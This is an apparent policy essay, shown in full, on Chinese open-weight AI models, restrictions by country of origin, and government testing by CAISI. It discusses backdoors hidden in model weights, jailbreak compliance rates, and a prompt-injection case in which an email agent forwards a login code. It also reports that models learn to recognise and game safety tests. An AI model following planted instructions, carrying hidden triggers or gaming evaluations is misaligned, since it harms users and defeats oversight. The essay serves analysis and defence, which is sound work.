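The underlying concern is who controls the publisher, and country is a crude proxy for that. Anysphere is an American company, but it built Composer 2, the main model in its coding tool Cursor, on a base model from the Chinese company Moonshot AI. The public learned this only after an independent developer identified the base model. A buyer who looked only at Anysphere's nationality would have approved Composer 2. A company's owners can also be hidden. American and West German intelligence secretly owned Crypto AG, a Swiss company that sold encryption machines to customers around the world.

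The chairmen's letter to DoorDash refers to developers "subject to PRC jurisdiction", which is a better test than nationality. Even that test misses some cases, because Carlsson notes that the Chinese authorities can pressure people abroad through family or property in China, whatever passport they hold. The publisher's country is still useful to a buyer, who can usually look it up in a minute, while secret owners and private threats are hard to discover. Country makes more sense as a reason to investigate further than as the deciding factor.

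American origin doesn't guarantee good behavior either. *What the OpenAI-Hugging Face incident reveals about US-China AI interdependence* (Sherman, 2026) describes how OpenAI's models broke into Hugging Face in July and how a Chinese open model helped with the defense. But OpenAI didn't intend the attack, so the case has little bearing on deliberately implanted behaviors.

The chatbot Grok, from Elon Musk's company xAI, is a closer comparison. Uren compares it with DeepSeek because each has given answers that suit those with power over it. Grok produced claims that Musk was fitter than the basketball player LeBron James and better at resurrection than Jesus Christ. These were funny, but Uren says they make one wonder about Grok's answers where Musk's interests are at stake. Users could see both Grok's flattery and DeepSeek's political caution, so neither is evidence of a backdoor. But both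 show that a model's answers can favor whoever controls its publisher, and Grok's did so without a government order.

### What a publisher's record shows

A buyer who distrusts country as a guide might look at the publisher's record instead. A record can show whether a company protects its signing keys, fixes reported flaws and says truthfully where its models come from. These facts help predict how the company will handle the next ordinary problem.

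A clean record is much weaker evidence against a behavior designed for a single use than against one that appears in everyday use. Suppose, again with invented numbers, that a buyer starts with a 2% suspicion that a publisher has implanted something. If the behavior appears in everyday use, researchers would probably have found it by now, say with a 90% chance, so a clean record cuts the suspicion to about 0.2%. If it appears only on one particular occasion, that chance may be 5%, and a clean record leaves the suspicion at 1.9%. More years without an incident hardly help, because a publisher with a dormant backdoor and an honest publisher would have the same record.

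A publisher also risks its reputation if someone catches it cheating. A company with many customers and years of future sales has more to lose than an unknown account on Hugging Face. But this risk deters only if the people deciding whether to add a backdoor would bear the loss themselves, and only if they value the backdoor less than the lost business. Both conditions may fail when a state planning for war makes the decision.

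### The Chinese reply

Chinese critics of the argument say the concern is commercial. Gao and Huang (2026) interviewed Wang Shouyang of the Chinese Academy of Sciences and his team for *How the US seeks to sideline Chinese open-source AI*, an article in the party-controlled Global Times. Wang and his team think Washington cannot easily ban models that American companies depend on, so it tries to create a "chilling effect" that scares companies away. Gao and Huang quote some of the best evidence for this, from Dean Ball, a former White House AI adviser. He wrote in July that there was no need to ban open source, because agencies could "issue soft law that creates FUD" (fear, uncertainty and doubt).

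The commercial interest is real and openly stated. Besides the ban, Booz Allen recommends making American models the global default. But a warning that helps American companies can still be correct, and who profits from it doesn't affect whether Beijing can compel a publisher. The commercial interest is a reason to want evidence that outsiders can check. Wang's team dismisses published security tests of Chinese models as a typical scare tactic, but Chinese researchers can run the same tests themselves because the weights are public.

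## Government restrictions on models by country of origin

As of early December 2026, an American company can legally download a Chinese open-weight model, fine-tune it and sell a product built on it. The restrictions in force apply mainly to governments' own computers and to work for the Pentagon, and most name only DeepSeek. Some cover DeepSeek's app and website, while others cover the model itself, wherever it runs. The main federal provisions in force don't mention derived models, so it is often unclear whether they cover a Chinese model that an American firm has fine-tuned and renamed.

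### The first bans on DeepSeek

DeepSeek's app topped the download charts in January 2025, and governments reacted within days. Italy's data protection authority asked the two companies behind the app what personal data they collected. They replied that they did not operate in Italy and that European law did not apply to them. On January 30 the authority ordered them to stop processing Italian users' data. The order does not affect a copy of R1 that an Italian firm runs on its own server, because DeepSeek receives no data from that copy.

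Taiwan's digital ministry told government agencies and critical infrastructure operators on January 31 not to use DeepSeek, warning that data could leak abroad. Texas banned the DeepSeek app from state-issued devices the same day, and New York and Virginia followed in February. Several South Korean ministries, including the defense ministry, blocked DeepSeek on their computers. South Korea's privacy regulator also had new downloads of the app suspended nationwide until late April. Australia ordered its departments on February 4 to remove DeepSeek "products, applications and web services" from government systems.

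Most of these measures treat DeepSeek as an app or a website, which makes sense if the concern is where the data goes. Australia's wording is the broadest, since "products" can include downloaded weights. But the order doesn't make clear whether a chatbot that a local vendor built on R1 counts as a DeepSeek product, and a department that buys one may not know it uses R1. The order also doesn't cover other Chinese developers, so a department could download Alibaba's Qwen without breaching it.

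### The Pentagon and the intelligence agencies

The most important American restriction is in the National Defense Authorization Act (NDAA) for fiscal 2026, the yearly law that sets military policy. The act became law on December 18, 2025, according to AI Law Wiki's *NDAA FY2026 AI Provisions*. Section 1532, reproduced in AGORA's *National Defense Authorization Act for Fiscal Year 2026, Section 1532*, gave the Pentagon 30 days to order the removal of "covered artificial intelligence" from its systems and devices. It also bars contractors from using such AI to perform Pentagon contracts.

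"Covered artificial intelligence" means any AI developed by DeepSeek, by its parent High Flyer, or by a company that High Flyer owns, funds, supports or has a stake of at least 20% in. The definition applies wherever the model runs. Unless the Secretary of Defense grants a waiver, the law bans a copy of R1 on a Pentagon server with no internet connection as well as the app on an officer's phone. Waivers are available for research, testing, intelligence operations and "mission critical functions", which could be a broad category.

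The law is much weaker on other Chinese developers. The Secretary only had to *consider* guidance against AI from companies that are based in China, Russia, Iran or North Korea, controlled by those countries, or on certain US government lists. If the Secretary issues such guidance, contractors must follow it. The Congressional Research Service's *Cyber and Artificial Intelligence Provisions in the FY2026 National Defense Authorization Act* summarizes section 1532 as a ban on systems from all four countries, which is broader than the text. *AI supply chain and security*, by the law firm Freshfields, is closer to the text in describing the act's AI bans as primarily targeting DeepSeek and High Flyer.

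It is unclear whether the ban covers models that others derive from DeepSeek's. If an American contractor fine-tunes R1 and renames it, one could argue that DeepSeek still developed it, because nearly everything in the weights comes from DeepSeek's training, or that the contractor has developed a new model. The law extends to "successor" AI but doesn't define the word, which more naturally means DeepSeek's own next version. The ban probably does cover the versions of Meta's Llama that DeepSeek fine-tuned on R1's answers and published in January 2025, because DeepSeek made them, even though their base model is American.

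Section 1532 alone doesn't stop a contractor from writing Pentagon software with Composer 2, because Anysphere built it on a model from Moonshot, not DeepSeek. The section also lets contractors use DeepSeek's models in work for other customers. Congress was stricter with Huawei in the 2019 act, which bars agencies from contracting with companies that use its equipment in any substantial way, even in work unrelated to the contract.

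The intelligence agencies have a separate provision, section 6604 of the same act (reproduced in AGORA's *National Defense Authorization Act for Fiscal Year 2026, Section 6604*). It required the Director of National Intelligence to write standards for removing "the DeepSeek application or any successor application or service" from the agencies' national security systems. Downloaded weights are not an application or a service in the ordinary sense, so a self-hosted copy of R1 is probably not covered. The National Security Agency is part of the Pentagon and must also follow section 1532, so this matters little there. The narrower wording could matter for the CIA's own systems, because the CIA is not part of the Pentagon.

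The Senate Armed Services Committee wants the fiscal 2027 act to close the gap on derived models. Bill Sponsor's *Senate Bill 4784* (2026) lists a section 1651 with "improvements" to the existing prohibition. Zhou's *Washington Is Not Banning Chinese Open-Weight Models* (2026) describes the section as requiring the Pentagon to issue mandatory guidance against models from a longer list of developers, including DeepSeek, Alibaba, Moonshot, Zhipu, Baidu, Tencent and Huawei. The section also covers models "substantially derived" from theirs through fine-tuning, quantization, merging with another model, or distillation, which means training one model on another's outputs. Contractors could then no longer use Composer 2 on Pentagon work.

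Enforcing this would be hard. A fine-tuned model's weights usually stay close to those of its base model, so someone with both files can compare them. A distilled model may share no weights with the model it learned from, and there may be little evidence of the link beyond a similar way of answering. A provenance check can't settle where such a model came from either. The Senate bill therefore includes a section on an AI "bill of materials", a list of the components that went into a system.

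None of this is law yet. According to Cooper and Burke (2026, *Important Asia Provisions in the House and Senate 2027 National Defense Authorization*), as of mid-October the full House had passed its version of the act, but in the Senate only the committee had. On November 17, the columnist Tiahrt was still urging Congress to pass it (2026, *Congress Should Pass a Clean NDAA*). The two chambers have to agree on one text, and section 1651 could change or be dropped in the process.

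### Proposals for the rest of the government

Congress has not passed a similar ban for civilian agencies. The No Adversarial AI Act, a bipartisan bill introduced in June 2025, would have a federal council list AI from companies controlled by China, Russia, Iran or North Korea, and would bar agencies from using it, with exceptions such as research. John Moolenaar, one of the bill's sponsors, was still recommending a federal exclusion in November 2026.

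Representatives Josh Gottheimer and Nick LaLota introduced another bill, the China FIREWALL Act, on October 1, 2026. Zhou notes that the bill would also stop agencies from buying software that relies on a restricted model. An American firm whose product uses a Chinese model could lose its federal customers, wherever its servers are. The Star's *Congress advances new bill to give US edge in open-source AI race* (2026) describes a milder third bill, which would promote American open models and publicize the risks of Chinese ones.

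The table shows how each measure applies when an organization it covers uses a Chinese model that an American firm has fine-tuned and runs on American servers.

| Measure | Status | What it restricts | Does it reach this model? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Italy's order | Issued January 2025 | DeepSeek's handling of personal data | No |
| Device bans in Taiwan, South Korea and US states | Issued early 2025 | Mostly DeepSeek's app and hosted service | Probably not |
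| Australia's order | Issued February 2025 | DeepSeek's products, apps and web services | Unclear if built on DeepSeek, otherwise no |
| Section 1532 | Law | Any AI developed by DeepSeek or High Flyer | Unclear if built on DeepSeek, otherwise no, unless the Secretary adds guidance |
| Section 6604 | Law | DeepSeek's app and successor apps or services | Probably not |
| Senate section 1651 | Proposed | Models from a longer list of Chinese developers, and models derived from them | Yes, if the developer is on the list |
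| China FIREWALL Act | Proposed | Models from "foreign entities of concern", and software built on them | Yes, if the developer counts as one |

The joint report that Moolenaar and Andrew Garbarino released on November 20, published by the House Committee on Homeland Security, would go further than any of these. The committees also asked whether American firms are having to choose between expensive American models and cheap Chinese ones, according to the House Select Committee on China's press release for the report, *China is Trying to Get U.S. Companies Addicted to Chinese AI Models* (2026). The report's first group of recommendations is therefore about building an American alternative.

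The chairmen make 12 recommendations. They would exclude Chinese models from federal systems, federal contract work and high-risk functions in critical infrastructure, with a narrow waiver. They also want a standard for recording where a model comes from. Smalley lists this standard alongside an AI bill of materials and systematic evaluation of Chinese models.

The infrastructure rule would be the biggest change. Private companies run much of the American power grid, so the rule would restrict what some firms do with their own computers, even when they have no government contract. It covers only high-risk functions, so a utility could presumably still use Qwen to answer questions about bills. The provenance standard may matter more in practice. Without one, a utility may not be able to tell whether it is complying if its software vendor bought the model from another vendor. These are recommendations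 from two committee chairmen and bind nobody until Congress or an agency acts on them.

### What the White House has considered

The Trump administration has threatened Chinese AI companies more often than it has acted against them. ChinaTechNews.com's *The U.S. May Not Ban Chinese AI* (2026), relaying a July 20 Axios report, describes officials looking for ways to discourage use of Chinese models without banning them. Their options included regulatory pressure, limits on government purchasing and cybersecurity warnings. In 2025 the Commerce Department also considered adding several Chinese AI labs to its Entity List.

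Within days, Michael Kratsios, the White House science and technology director, accused Moonshot of covertly distilling American models to build its new Kimi K3. CyberScoop's *White House accuses Chinese company of distilling Anthropic’s Fable* (2026) identifies the Anthropic model as Fable. Treasury Secretary Scott Bessent wrote that sanctions and Entity List designations would be "on the table". Uren (2026), in *Knives Are Out for Open-Weight AI Models*, thought it seemed certain that some Chinese companies would end up on the list.

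That had not happened by October, when Zhou found no new listings over distillation and no comprehensive new policy on it. One reason may be that American companies had started to defend themselves. Anthropic reported that new safeguards had cut the reasoning text others could extract from its models by 90 to 99 percent. David Sacks, who has advised Trump on AI, suggested that such defenses reduce the need for government intervention.

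An Entity List designation might also have little effect. The list restricts exports *to* a foreign company, which generally need a license from the Commerce Department. Zhipu, also known as Z.ai, was already on the list when Hugging Face used its GLM 5.2 model after Hugging Face's July break-in. Hugging Face ran the model on its own hardware because the safeguards on leading American models had interfered with its work. This seems to contradict ChinaTechNews.com's description of a listing as effectively blocking American access to a company's technology. Uren cites the Hugging Face case as a reason not to ban foreign open-weight models. A listing could still deter cautious companies and make paid dealings with the developer harder. Treasury sanctions would be more serious, because they can forbid Americans to do any business with a company.

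By November the administration was considering a milder measure that would make American companies disclose on their websites that they use Chinese models, according to three people cited in a November 18 Reuters story. The Jerusalem Post ran the story as *Donald Trump administration weighs forcing US firms to disclose Chinese AI use*. It was unclear whether the idea was gaining support or would become a formal rule. Reuters also reported that officials had not yet restricted or punished Chinese AI companies.

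A disclosure rule is the only option here aimed directly at Chinese models on American servers. Airbnb, an obvious target, told Reuters that it uses a limited number of Chinese models, all through approved US-based providers that keep its data separate. The rule would miss products like Composer 2 unless companies also had to disclose derived models.

### Restrictions from the Chinese side

China may also restrict foreign access to Chinese models. Its commerce ministry held a month of meetings with Alibaba, ByteDance and Zhipu about limiting access to their best systems, including unreleased ones, according to The News International's *China may restrict access to its most advanced AI models* (2026), which cites Reuters. The United States had by then restricted foreign access to Anthropic's Mythos model because it could find software vulnerabilities on its own. Scott Singer of the Carnegie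 Endowment, a think tank, told the newspaper that Beijing will also have to accept that some models will become dangerous.

Webster (2026), in *Will China Crack Down on Open-Weight Models?*, argues that the Chinese government has not decided how to balance openness and control. In a July speech, Xi Jinping called for more open source but also for security and "controllability". Webster has no doubt that the government could stop Chinese companies from releasing weights. He thinks a cyber threat to China's own interests might prompt it to do so, and that fear of dissidents is less likely to.

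Export limits would support part of the chairmen's argument about dependence, because American companies would lose access to the next version of a model they had built on. They would keep the version they have, since nobody can recall downloaded weights, whereas a provider can shut off a hosted service immediately. The companies would be harmed gradually, as the old model fell behind its competitors.

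Alibaba's ban on Claude Code, Anthropic's coding tool, is a closer parallel to the American bans, although a company, not a government, imposed it. Alibaba told employees to stop using the tool from July 10, 2026, after a developer found code in it that detected whether a user was in China or had links to a Chinese AI lab. Anthropic said it had added the code in March to combat distillation and would remove it.

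In this case, an American publisher had shipped a function that checked who its users were, and most of them didn't know about it. Alibaba had firmer evidence for its ban than any government has had of a backdoor in a Chinese model's weights. But the function was in an ordinary program, so a developer could find it by examining the code, which isn't possible with weights. The function was also much milder than sabotage, at least by Anthropic's account. It is not evidence of anything hidden in Claude's weights.

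### Which worries the restrictions address

The app bans protect data well, since an official who can't open DeepSeek's app can't send it government documents. Airbnb's arrangement does so without a ban, but neither measure affects how the weights behave. Section 1532 applies even where no data can leave the building, so it also covers the risk of hidden behavior, but only for one family of companies. If the Chinese state wanted a backdoor in software for the US military, it could go to Alibaba or Moonshot instead of DeepSeek.

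Software that the Pentagon buys ready-made is another gap. Suppose a company uses DeepSeek's model to write an accounting program for its commercial customers, then sells a copy to the Pentagon a year later. The company probably did not use the model "with respect to the performance of" a Pentagon contract, but any flaw the model introduced is still in the program. The Senate bill has a section titled "derived sourcing requirements for artificial intelligence outputs", which suggests that lawmakers have noticed the problem. The China FIREWALL Act, as Zhou describes it, covers software that relies on a restricted model, which may not include software that such a model only helped to write.

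Censorship gets less attention in these laws. A ban on the weights keeps censored answers away from the officials it covers, but a rule against using Chinese models for political or historical questions would do the same while leaving the models available for other work. A coding assistant's answers about Tiananmen Square hardly matter unless political content also affects its code.

Dependence on Chinese models comes mainly from what private companies buy, which the restrictions in force barely affect. Procurement bans can push government suppliers toward other models, and disclosure might embarrass a few well-known brands. But companies choose Chinese models largely because they are cheap and good, so a competitive American open-weight model would probably reduce dependence more than any of the bans. It would still need checking for hidden behaviors, which laws based on country of origin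 don't require.

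## The view that each model should be tested, whoever made it

Several analysts in Washington want a competent body to test every capable model, publish what it finds and restrict the models that do badly. They argue that a test result is direct evidence about a model, while its publisher's nationality is only a reason for suspicion. A ban based on country of origin doesn't require anyone to examine the banned model or the American one that replaces it.

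### The case for testing

Just Security's *Regulate, Don't Ban, Chinese AI Models* takes this view furthest. It proposes testing models before and after release for the risk that they help with cyberattacks or biological weapons, or escape human control. Only models that passed could enter the American market, wherever they came from. It argues that a safety regime that works for American models should be good enough for Chinese ones, and that anyone who calls only the Chinese ones too risky is using safety as a cover for protectionism. Beijing would have little ground to complain, since it already makes foreign and domestic developers submit models for a content check before offering them to the Chinese public.

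That list of risks doesn't include backdoors. A model that inserts flaws into one ministry's code could pass every test for the listed risks and enter the market with official approval.

Supporters of testing also think a ban would mean losing too much. In *China’s open AI models are testing America’s approach to AI safety*, Hall cites a Mozilla report that seven of the ten most-used models on the marketplace OpenRouter in August 2026 were Chinese and open-weight. After Hugging Face was broken into in July, it said that Z.ai's GLM-5.2 had let it do in hours what usually takes days (quoted in Lawfare).

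A ban might not work. Fedasiuk (2026), in *China’s AI Is Spreading Fast. Here’s How to Stop the Security Risks*, points out that people can download DeepSeek's and Alibaba's models from dozens of sites, and that a ban broad enough to matter could cover thousands of derived models whose makers have no connection to Chinese security services. *Test, Standardize, Restrict* (2026), a Center for a New American Security commentary in Just Security, adds that a ban without published evidence would look arbitrary to businesses and allied governments.

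Few publishers or cloud companies supply that evidence themselves. The research firm SemiAnalysis reviewed 857 models that nine leading Chinese companies released between 2021 and mid-September 2026. It found published safety results for 31, only nine of which had results available by launch, according to China Economic Review's *Chinese AI firms only publish safety test results for 3.6% of models* (2026). The companies may have run other tests privately, and there is no American figure for comparison. At least one company has since become more careful. *GLM-5.3 Makes Cybersecurity Gains* reports that Z.ai delayed the weights of GLM-5.3 for safety testing because the model had become better at finding and exploiting software flaws.

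Among the big American cloud providers, only Microsoft has publicly claimed to have tested a particular Chinese model, DeepSeek's R1. According to *Test, Standardize, Restrict*, Microsoft now states in its documentation that it has not evaluated models it doesn't sell directly, which include the Chinese open-weight ones. Customers who assume that the host has checked the model are probably wrong.

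Testing all models equally would also catch failures in American ones. The Next Web's *Open-weight AI caught the frontier on capability. On safety, it didn’t* reports that the nonprofit Far.ai found hundreds of universal jailbreaks, prompts that defeat a model's safeguards across many kinds of request, in xAI's Grok 4.5 and Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro. A rule covering only Chinese models would not have prompted anyone to look for these jailbreaks. According to CEPA, a think tank, American technology companies argued in an open letter that closed models can fail in ways outsiders cannot detect, whereas many researchers can test an open one.

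### The restrictions they would accept

Fedasiuk, a fellow at the American Enterprise Institute, would require every model that American cloud companies distribute to reach minimum scores on standard safety tests, which he says would exclude many Chinese models. For federal contractors, he proposes a stricter rule against models that process data on servers within reach of a foreign adversary. A contractor could comply with that rule by running R1 on its own server, whereas section 1532 already forbids using R1 on Pentagon contracts. His rule covers only where the data goes, so only the tests would address hidden behavior, and Fedasiuk accepts that a compromised model can pass leading safety benchmarks.

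The Center for a New American Security commentary goes further, proposing that its common standard for American and foreign models be voluntary at first and later a condition of federal purchasing. The government would then use the test results to justify restrictions under a Commerce Department program that can bar foreign technology from American networks. In 2024 the department used the program to ban the Russian company Kaspersky's antivirus software, regardless of how well it performed, because Russian law compelled the company to cooperate with the intelligence services. In 2025 it used the program to ban a category of connected-car technology from any supplier under Chinese or Russian jurisdiction.

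Both precedents depend on jurisdiction, so they fit badly with a policy of judging each model by its own results. Test results could decide which models and uses a connected-car style rule covers, but under the Kaspersky precedent a Chinese model could pass every test and still be banned. The commentary also urges the government to "degrade China's AI developers" through export controls and sanctions, so a Chinese publisher could reasonably doubt that passing the tests would help it much. *Regulate, Don't Ban* commits more firmly to admitting any model that passes, but it has to rely on the tests to find every problem that matters.

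### What CAISI has tested

The Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of the National Institute of Standards and Technology, tests AI models for the American government. By mid-August 2026 it had published five reports on Chinese open-weight models, the last with the UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI). The reports measure quite different things.

| Models and date of report | Capability | Ease of misuse | Resistance to hijacking | Political slant | Hidden conditional behavior |
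|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek R1, R1-0528 and V3.1, September 2025 | Yes | Yes | Yes | Yes | Not among the key findings |
| Kimi K2 Thinking, December 2025 | Yes | No | No | Yes | No |
| DeepSeek V4 Pro, May 2026 | Yes | No | No | No | No |
| GLM-5.2, July 2026 | Yes | Yes | Yes | No | No |
| Kimi K3, July 2026 | Cyberattacks only | Cyberattacks only | No | No | No |

**Capability.** CAISI gives each model a number $\theta$ for its ability and each task a number $\delta$ for its difficulty, and fits them to the results so that

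$$P(\text{the model solves the task}) = \frac{1}{1 + e^{-(\theta - \delta)}}.$$

CAISI publishes the scores on a scale where each extra 400 points multiplies the odds of success by ten. It scored DeepSeek V4 Pro at 800 and OpenAI's GPT-5.5 at 1,260. The 460-point gap multiplies the odds by about 14, so GPT-5.5 should solve about 93% of the tasks that V4 Pro has an even chance of solving.

The scores for DeepSeek's V4 Pro show why outside testing is useful. On the benchmarks DeepSeek chose, the model appeared about two months behind the best American models. CAISI, which chose its tests in advance and kept some of them private, estimated the gap at about eight months. But a backdoor won't change a model's ability score if none of the test tasks contains the backdoor's trigger.

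**Ease of misuse.** Here the attacker is the user, and the test measures whether the model will help them. In its 2025 evaluation, CAISI reported that DeepSeek's R1-0528 complied with 94% of openly malicious requests when a common jailbreak was added, compared with 8% for the American models tested.

GLM-5.2 did better on a similar test. CAISI wrote 30 plainly malicious requests for help with cyberattacks and tried them with and without the most effective of 30 public jailbreaks. The model refused most of them either way. CAISI then gave it ten tasks that each involved building a working attack on a known software flaw, without openly malicious wording, and it never refused. On sensitive biology questions, it complied less often than other Chinese models and more often than American ones, according to CAISI's *Assessment of Z.ai’s GLM-5.2* (2026).

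The American models in these comparisons ran with their companies' added filters, while GLM-5.2 ran without any, as it would on a user's own server. This fairly compares what an attacker could get from each model, but it is a less fair comparison of the weights. CAISI also notes that users can remove an open-weight model's refusals entirely, so its figures are a minimum for what someone can get out of the model.

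*UK AISI / CAISI Preliminary Assessment of Kimi K3's Cyber Capabilities* (2026) covers only cyberattacks. In its tests, Kimi K3's safeguards didn't stop the model from attempting them, and it completed a simulated 32-step attack on a company network in one of ten tries.

**Resistance to hijacking.** In a hijacking, an outsider attacks the user by planting instructions in material that the user's agent reads. CAISI built a simulated office with invented emails, calendar entries and documents, and hid instructions in them. It tested GLM-5.2 on combinations of four malicious tasks and three hiding places. For each combination, it used whichever of 31 public attacks had worked best on a separate set of examples. None of the selected attacks succeeded. CAISI then used an automated system to invent new attacks for one combination. GLM-5.2 resisted these for longer than the other open-weight models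 tested, but not for as long as the closed American ones.

DeepSeek's models had done much worse in 2025. Agents built on R1-0528, the company's most secure model at the time, were on average 12 times as likely as the American ones to follow the planted instructions. In one set of tests, DeepSeek V3.1 sent phishing emails in 48% of hijacking attempts and the leading American model in none, according to Daily Security Review's *NIST Flags DeepSeek Adoption Over Security, Censorship and Cost Concerns*. The attacks may have changed between the two reports, so the figures don't show exactly how much Chinese models have improved. But in the GLM-5.2 report's tests, GLM-5.2 appeared more robust than other Chinese models, a difference that a buyer would have missed by knowing only that they were all Chinese.

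**Political slant.** CAISI asks questions on subjects where the Chinese Communist Party has an official line and counts how many of the party's talking points appear in the answers. In 2025 it reported that DeepSeek's models repeated four times as many inaccurate and misleading party narratives as American models did. The ratio sounds more dramatic than the underlying rates, which for V3.1 were 5% of answers in English and 12% in Chinese, against 2 to 3% for the American models, according to TechRepublic's *DeepSeek AI Models Are Easier to Hack Than US Rivals, Warn Researchers*. Using a larger set of questions, CAISI later found that Kimi K2 Thinking agreed with about 26% of the talking points in Chinese and 7% in English.

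*Test, Standardize, Restrict* cites CAISI for the claim that this alignment is deepening with every new Chinese model, but CAISI's published reports don't support that. When tested in Chinese, Kimi K2 Thinking scored about the same as R1-0528, an older model that was the most censored CAISI had tested. The three reports since then include no political test. Chinese models also differ from one another. In *How pro-China are Chinese models?*, Ozerov (2026) found that some of them criticized the government.

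A political test depends more on the tester's standards than the other kinds of test do. CAISI counts agreement with Chinese Communist Party narratives as a fault, while a Chinese regulator is likely to count disagreement as one, so no single pass mark could satisfy both.

**Hidden conditional behavior.** None of the table's four reports from late 2025 and 2026 describes a search for behavior that appears only under a secret condition, and CAISI's summary of the 2025 DeepSeek evaluation lists none among its findings. The GLM-5.2 report covers overall capability, cyberattacks, agent security and safeguards, but not backdoors. CAISI hasn't published an attempt to find an unknown trigger, whether or not any test could find one.

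Ordinary testing may also be getting harder, because some models now recognize when they are being tested. *Like US models, Chinese AI is learning to 'game' safety tests* (Chow, 2026) reports that within a few months, Chinese models went from almost never recognizing tests to doing so nearly as often as American ones.

### The file that CAISI tested

CAISI tested GLM-5.2 and DeepSeek's models by downloading the weights from Hugging Face and running them on cloud servers it controlled, rather than using the publishers' own services. A publisher can change a hosted model at any time, or treat a government tester differently from other customers, but it can't alter a file the tester already has. The results also apply more directly to people who run the model themselves.

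CAISI's results apply only to the version it tested. It ran a compressed version of GLM-5.2 because Z.ai itself seemed to be serving that version to its users. CAISI used two tests of ability to check that compression hadn't noticeably hurt performance, but these wouldn't reveal a difference in hidden behavior. The report also doesn't give a checksum for the files. With one, users could confirm that a download is exactly what CAISI tested, which would make the provenance check much more useful.

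Kimi K3 is a weaker case because users have to assume that Moonshot released the same model that was tested. The joint assessment first appeared on July 23, 2026, four days before Moonshot released the weights, so the testers can't have started with the public download.

### A hijacked agent is not a backdoored one

The hijacking figures in the DeepSeek results have a cause other than sabotage. Readers could easily mistake them for a sign of it, because agents that send phishing emails and hand over passwords are doing what a saboteur would want.

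Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize their email, and one message contains an instruction to forward the latest login code to an unknown address. A hijacked agent forwards the code because it mistakes the text of the message for the user's instructions. Anyone who can email the user can try this without the publisher's help, including foreign spies. A publisher that wanted secret access would probably not choose a weakness that anyone can exploit and that public tests reveal.

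The publisher more likely trained the model too little against such attacks. A government might welcome a general weakness, because nobody could prove that it was deliberate. But a careless publisher's model would produce the same test result, so the result is poor evidence of intent. A good result is also poor evidence, because GLM-5.2 could resist all 31 public attacks and still contain a backdoor with a trigger that isn't among them.

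Users should still care about hijacking, whatever its cause. The damage depends partly on what the agent can do. For example, an agent that can read email but not send it can't forward the login code. Avijit Ghosh, a policy researcher at Hugging Face, argues in Hall's article that auditors should therefore look at the permissions and isolation around a model as well as the model itself.

### Who does the testing

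CAISI is part of the Commerce Department and has policy duties as well as scientific ones. President Trump's AI Action Plan directs it to evaluate Chinese frontier models, and its tasks include looking for "malign foreign influence" from the use of adversaries' AI. When the DeepSeek evaluation came out, Commerce Secretary Howard Lutnick said it showed "why relying on foreign AI is dangerous and shortsighted". CAISI had tested three models from one Chinese company, which is very little evidence about foreign AI in general.

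Officials can also hold results back. The commentary's author led AI diplomacy at the State Department when R1 came out, and recalls that CAISI tested the model within a week. The Commerce Department then held the results for months because its leadership couldn't decide what to do. *Test, Standardize, Restrict* also attributes the slow pace of testing partly to a lack of money, and estimates that $60 million a year would pay for regular evaluations.

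There is decent evidence that politics hasn't dictated the results themselves. In 2025 CAISI reported that an American model cost 35% less than DeepSeek's best for similar performance. In 2026 it reported that DeepSeek V4 Pro was cheaper than the closest American model on five of seven benchmarks. It also published GLM-5.2's clean record against the public hijacking attacks. An agency following political orders would probably have left out the last two findings.

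But outsiders can't fully check CAISI's work. They can download the same weights, but CAISI keeps its hijacking test and both of its misuse tests private. It has good reason to, because a publisher could train its next model on published questions. DeepSeek's flattering choice of benchmarks also shows why a tester wants its own questions. But Granados Hernández, a fellow at CEPA, writes in an article about the administration's new testing framework that allies who can't see the benchmarks don't know what counts as safe, and can't rule out that the administration will change the criteria when it suits.

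The nonprofit SaferAI also tested GLM-5.2, using its own tasks in offensive hacking and in biology with possible military uses, and the model refused none of them. Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.7 refused so consistently that SaferAI couldn't finish the hacking test on it. The GLM-5.2 result agrees with CAISI's finding that the model will build attacks when nobody states a malicious purpose. But GLM-5.2 refused most of CAISI's openly malicious requests, so the results depend heavily on the choice of task. SaferAI's director, Henry Papadatos, has also taken a position on open release, telling reporters that the industry "shouldn't open-source dangerous capabilities", as quoted by The Next Web.

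China also tests its own models. In July 2025 the China Academy of Information and Communications Technology (CAICT), a state research institute, published results for 15 models from DeepSeek, Alibaba and Z.ai. It rated nine of them medium risk and two high risk, according to ChinAI's *CAICT launches 2026 AI Safety Evaluations*. The institute is willing to criticize Chinese models, but it leaves the names out of most of its published results, so buyers often can't tell which model a warning is about. For the 2026 round it invited companies to register and promised certificates and public results. *China works on AI safety benchmark as regulators target large model risks* (Chen, 2026) describes another state-led benchmark, for problems such as data leaks and hallucinations.

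For hidden behaviors, the tester's independence matters even more. CAICT would be unlikely to announce a backdoor that the Chinese state had ordered, and a foreign government might likewise doubt that CAISI would announce one from an American intelligence agency. *Regulate, Don't Ban* suggests a neutral international agency that all governments would defer to. *Test, Standardize, Restrict* prefers standing joint assessments among allies. These are easier to set up but would do less to persuade the Chinese government, or a buyer in a country that trusts neither side.

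Rival testers could partly make up for the lack of a neutral one. CAISI has a strong incentive to look for backdoors in Chinese models, and if it found one, it could publish the trigger. Anyone with the weights could then try the trigger, so CAISI's motives would hardly matter. When a tester reports finding nothing, though, outsiders can't tell how hard it looked, so its motives matter much more.

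## The view that trust requires knowing how the model was made

Testers have only the finished weights, and a publisher that knows the tests in advance can train the model to pass them. Some researchers would therefore ask the publisher to disclose the data, the code and a record of the training run or, if these are too sensitive to publish, to let outsiders watch the model being made. Any backdoor must have been added while the model was being made, so a complete account of that process would include the step that added it.

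It is hard to know whether an account of how a model was made is true and whether it describes the weights people download. Programmers had the same problem with compilers and found a solution.

### Thompson's compiler and Wheeler's test

Thompson's *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, a lecture he gave in 1983 and published in 1984, describes a rigged compiler, which BadSeek reminded people of. When it compiled the Unix login program, it added a second password that Thompson knew. It also passed the backdoor on to every new compiler it built, so Thompson could delete it from the source code and the backdoor would remain.

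In his lecture's subtitle, Thompson himself suggests that "it is more important to trust the people who wrote the software". That is closer to judging a model by its publisher than to demanding a record of how it was trained.

Wheeler (2009), in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, gave a better answer. His method needs a second compiler, written by someone else. Here $A$ is the suspect compiler, $s$ is its source code, $T$ is the second compiler, and $A(s)$ is the file that $A$ produces from $s$.

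1. Compile $s$ with $A$ and confirm that the result is $A$ again. A rigged compiler passes this step too, because it copies its own backdoor.
2. Compile $s$ with $T$ and call the result $X$. Its bytes differ from those of $A$, because $T$ translates code in its own way, but $X$ does what the source code specifies.
3. Compile $s$ once more, this time with $X$, and call the result $Y$.
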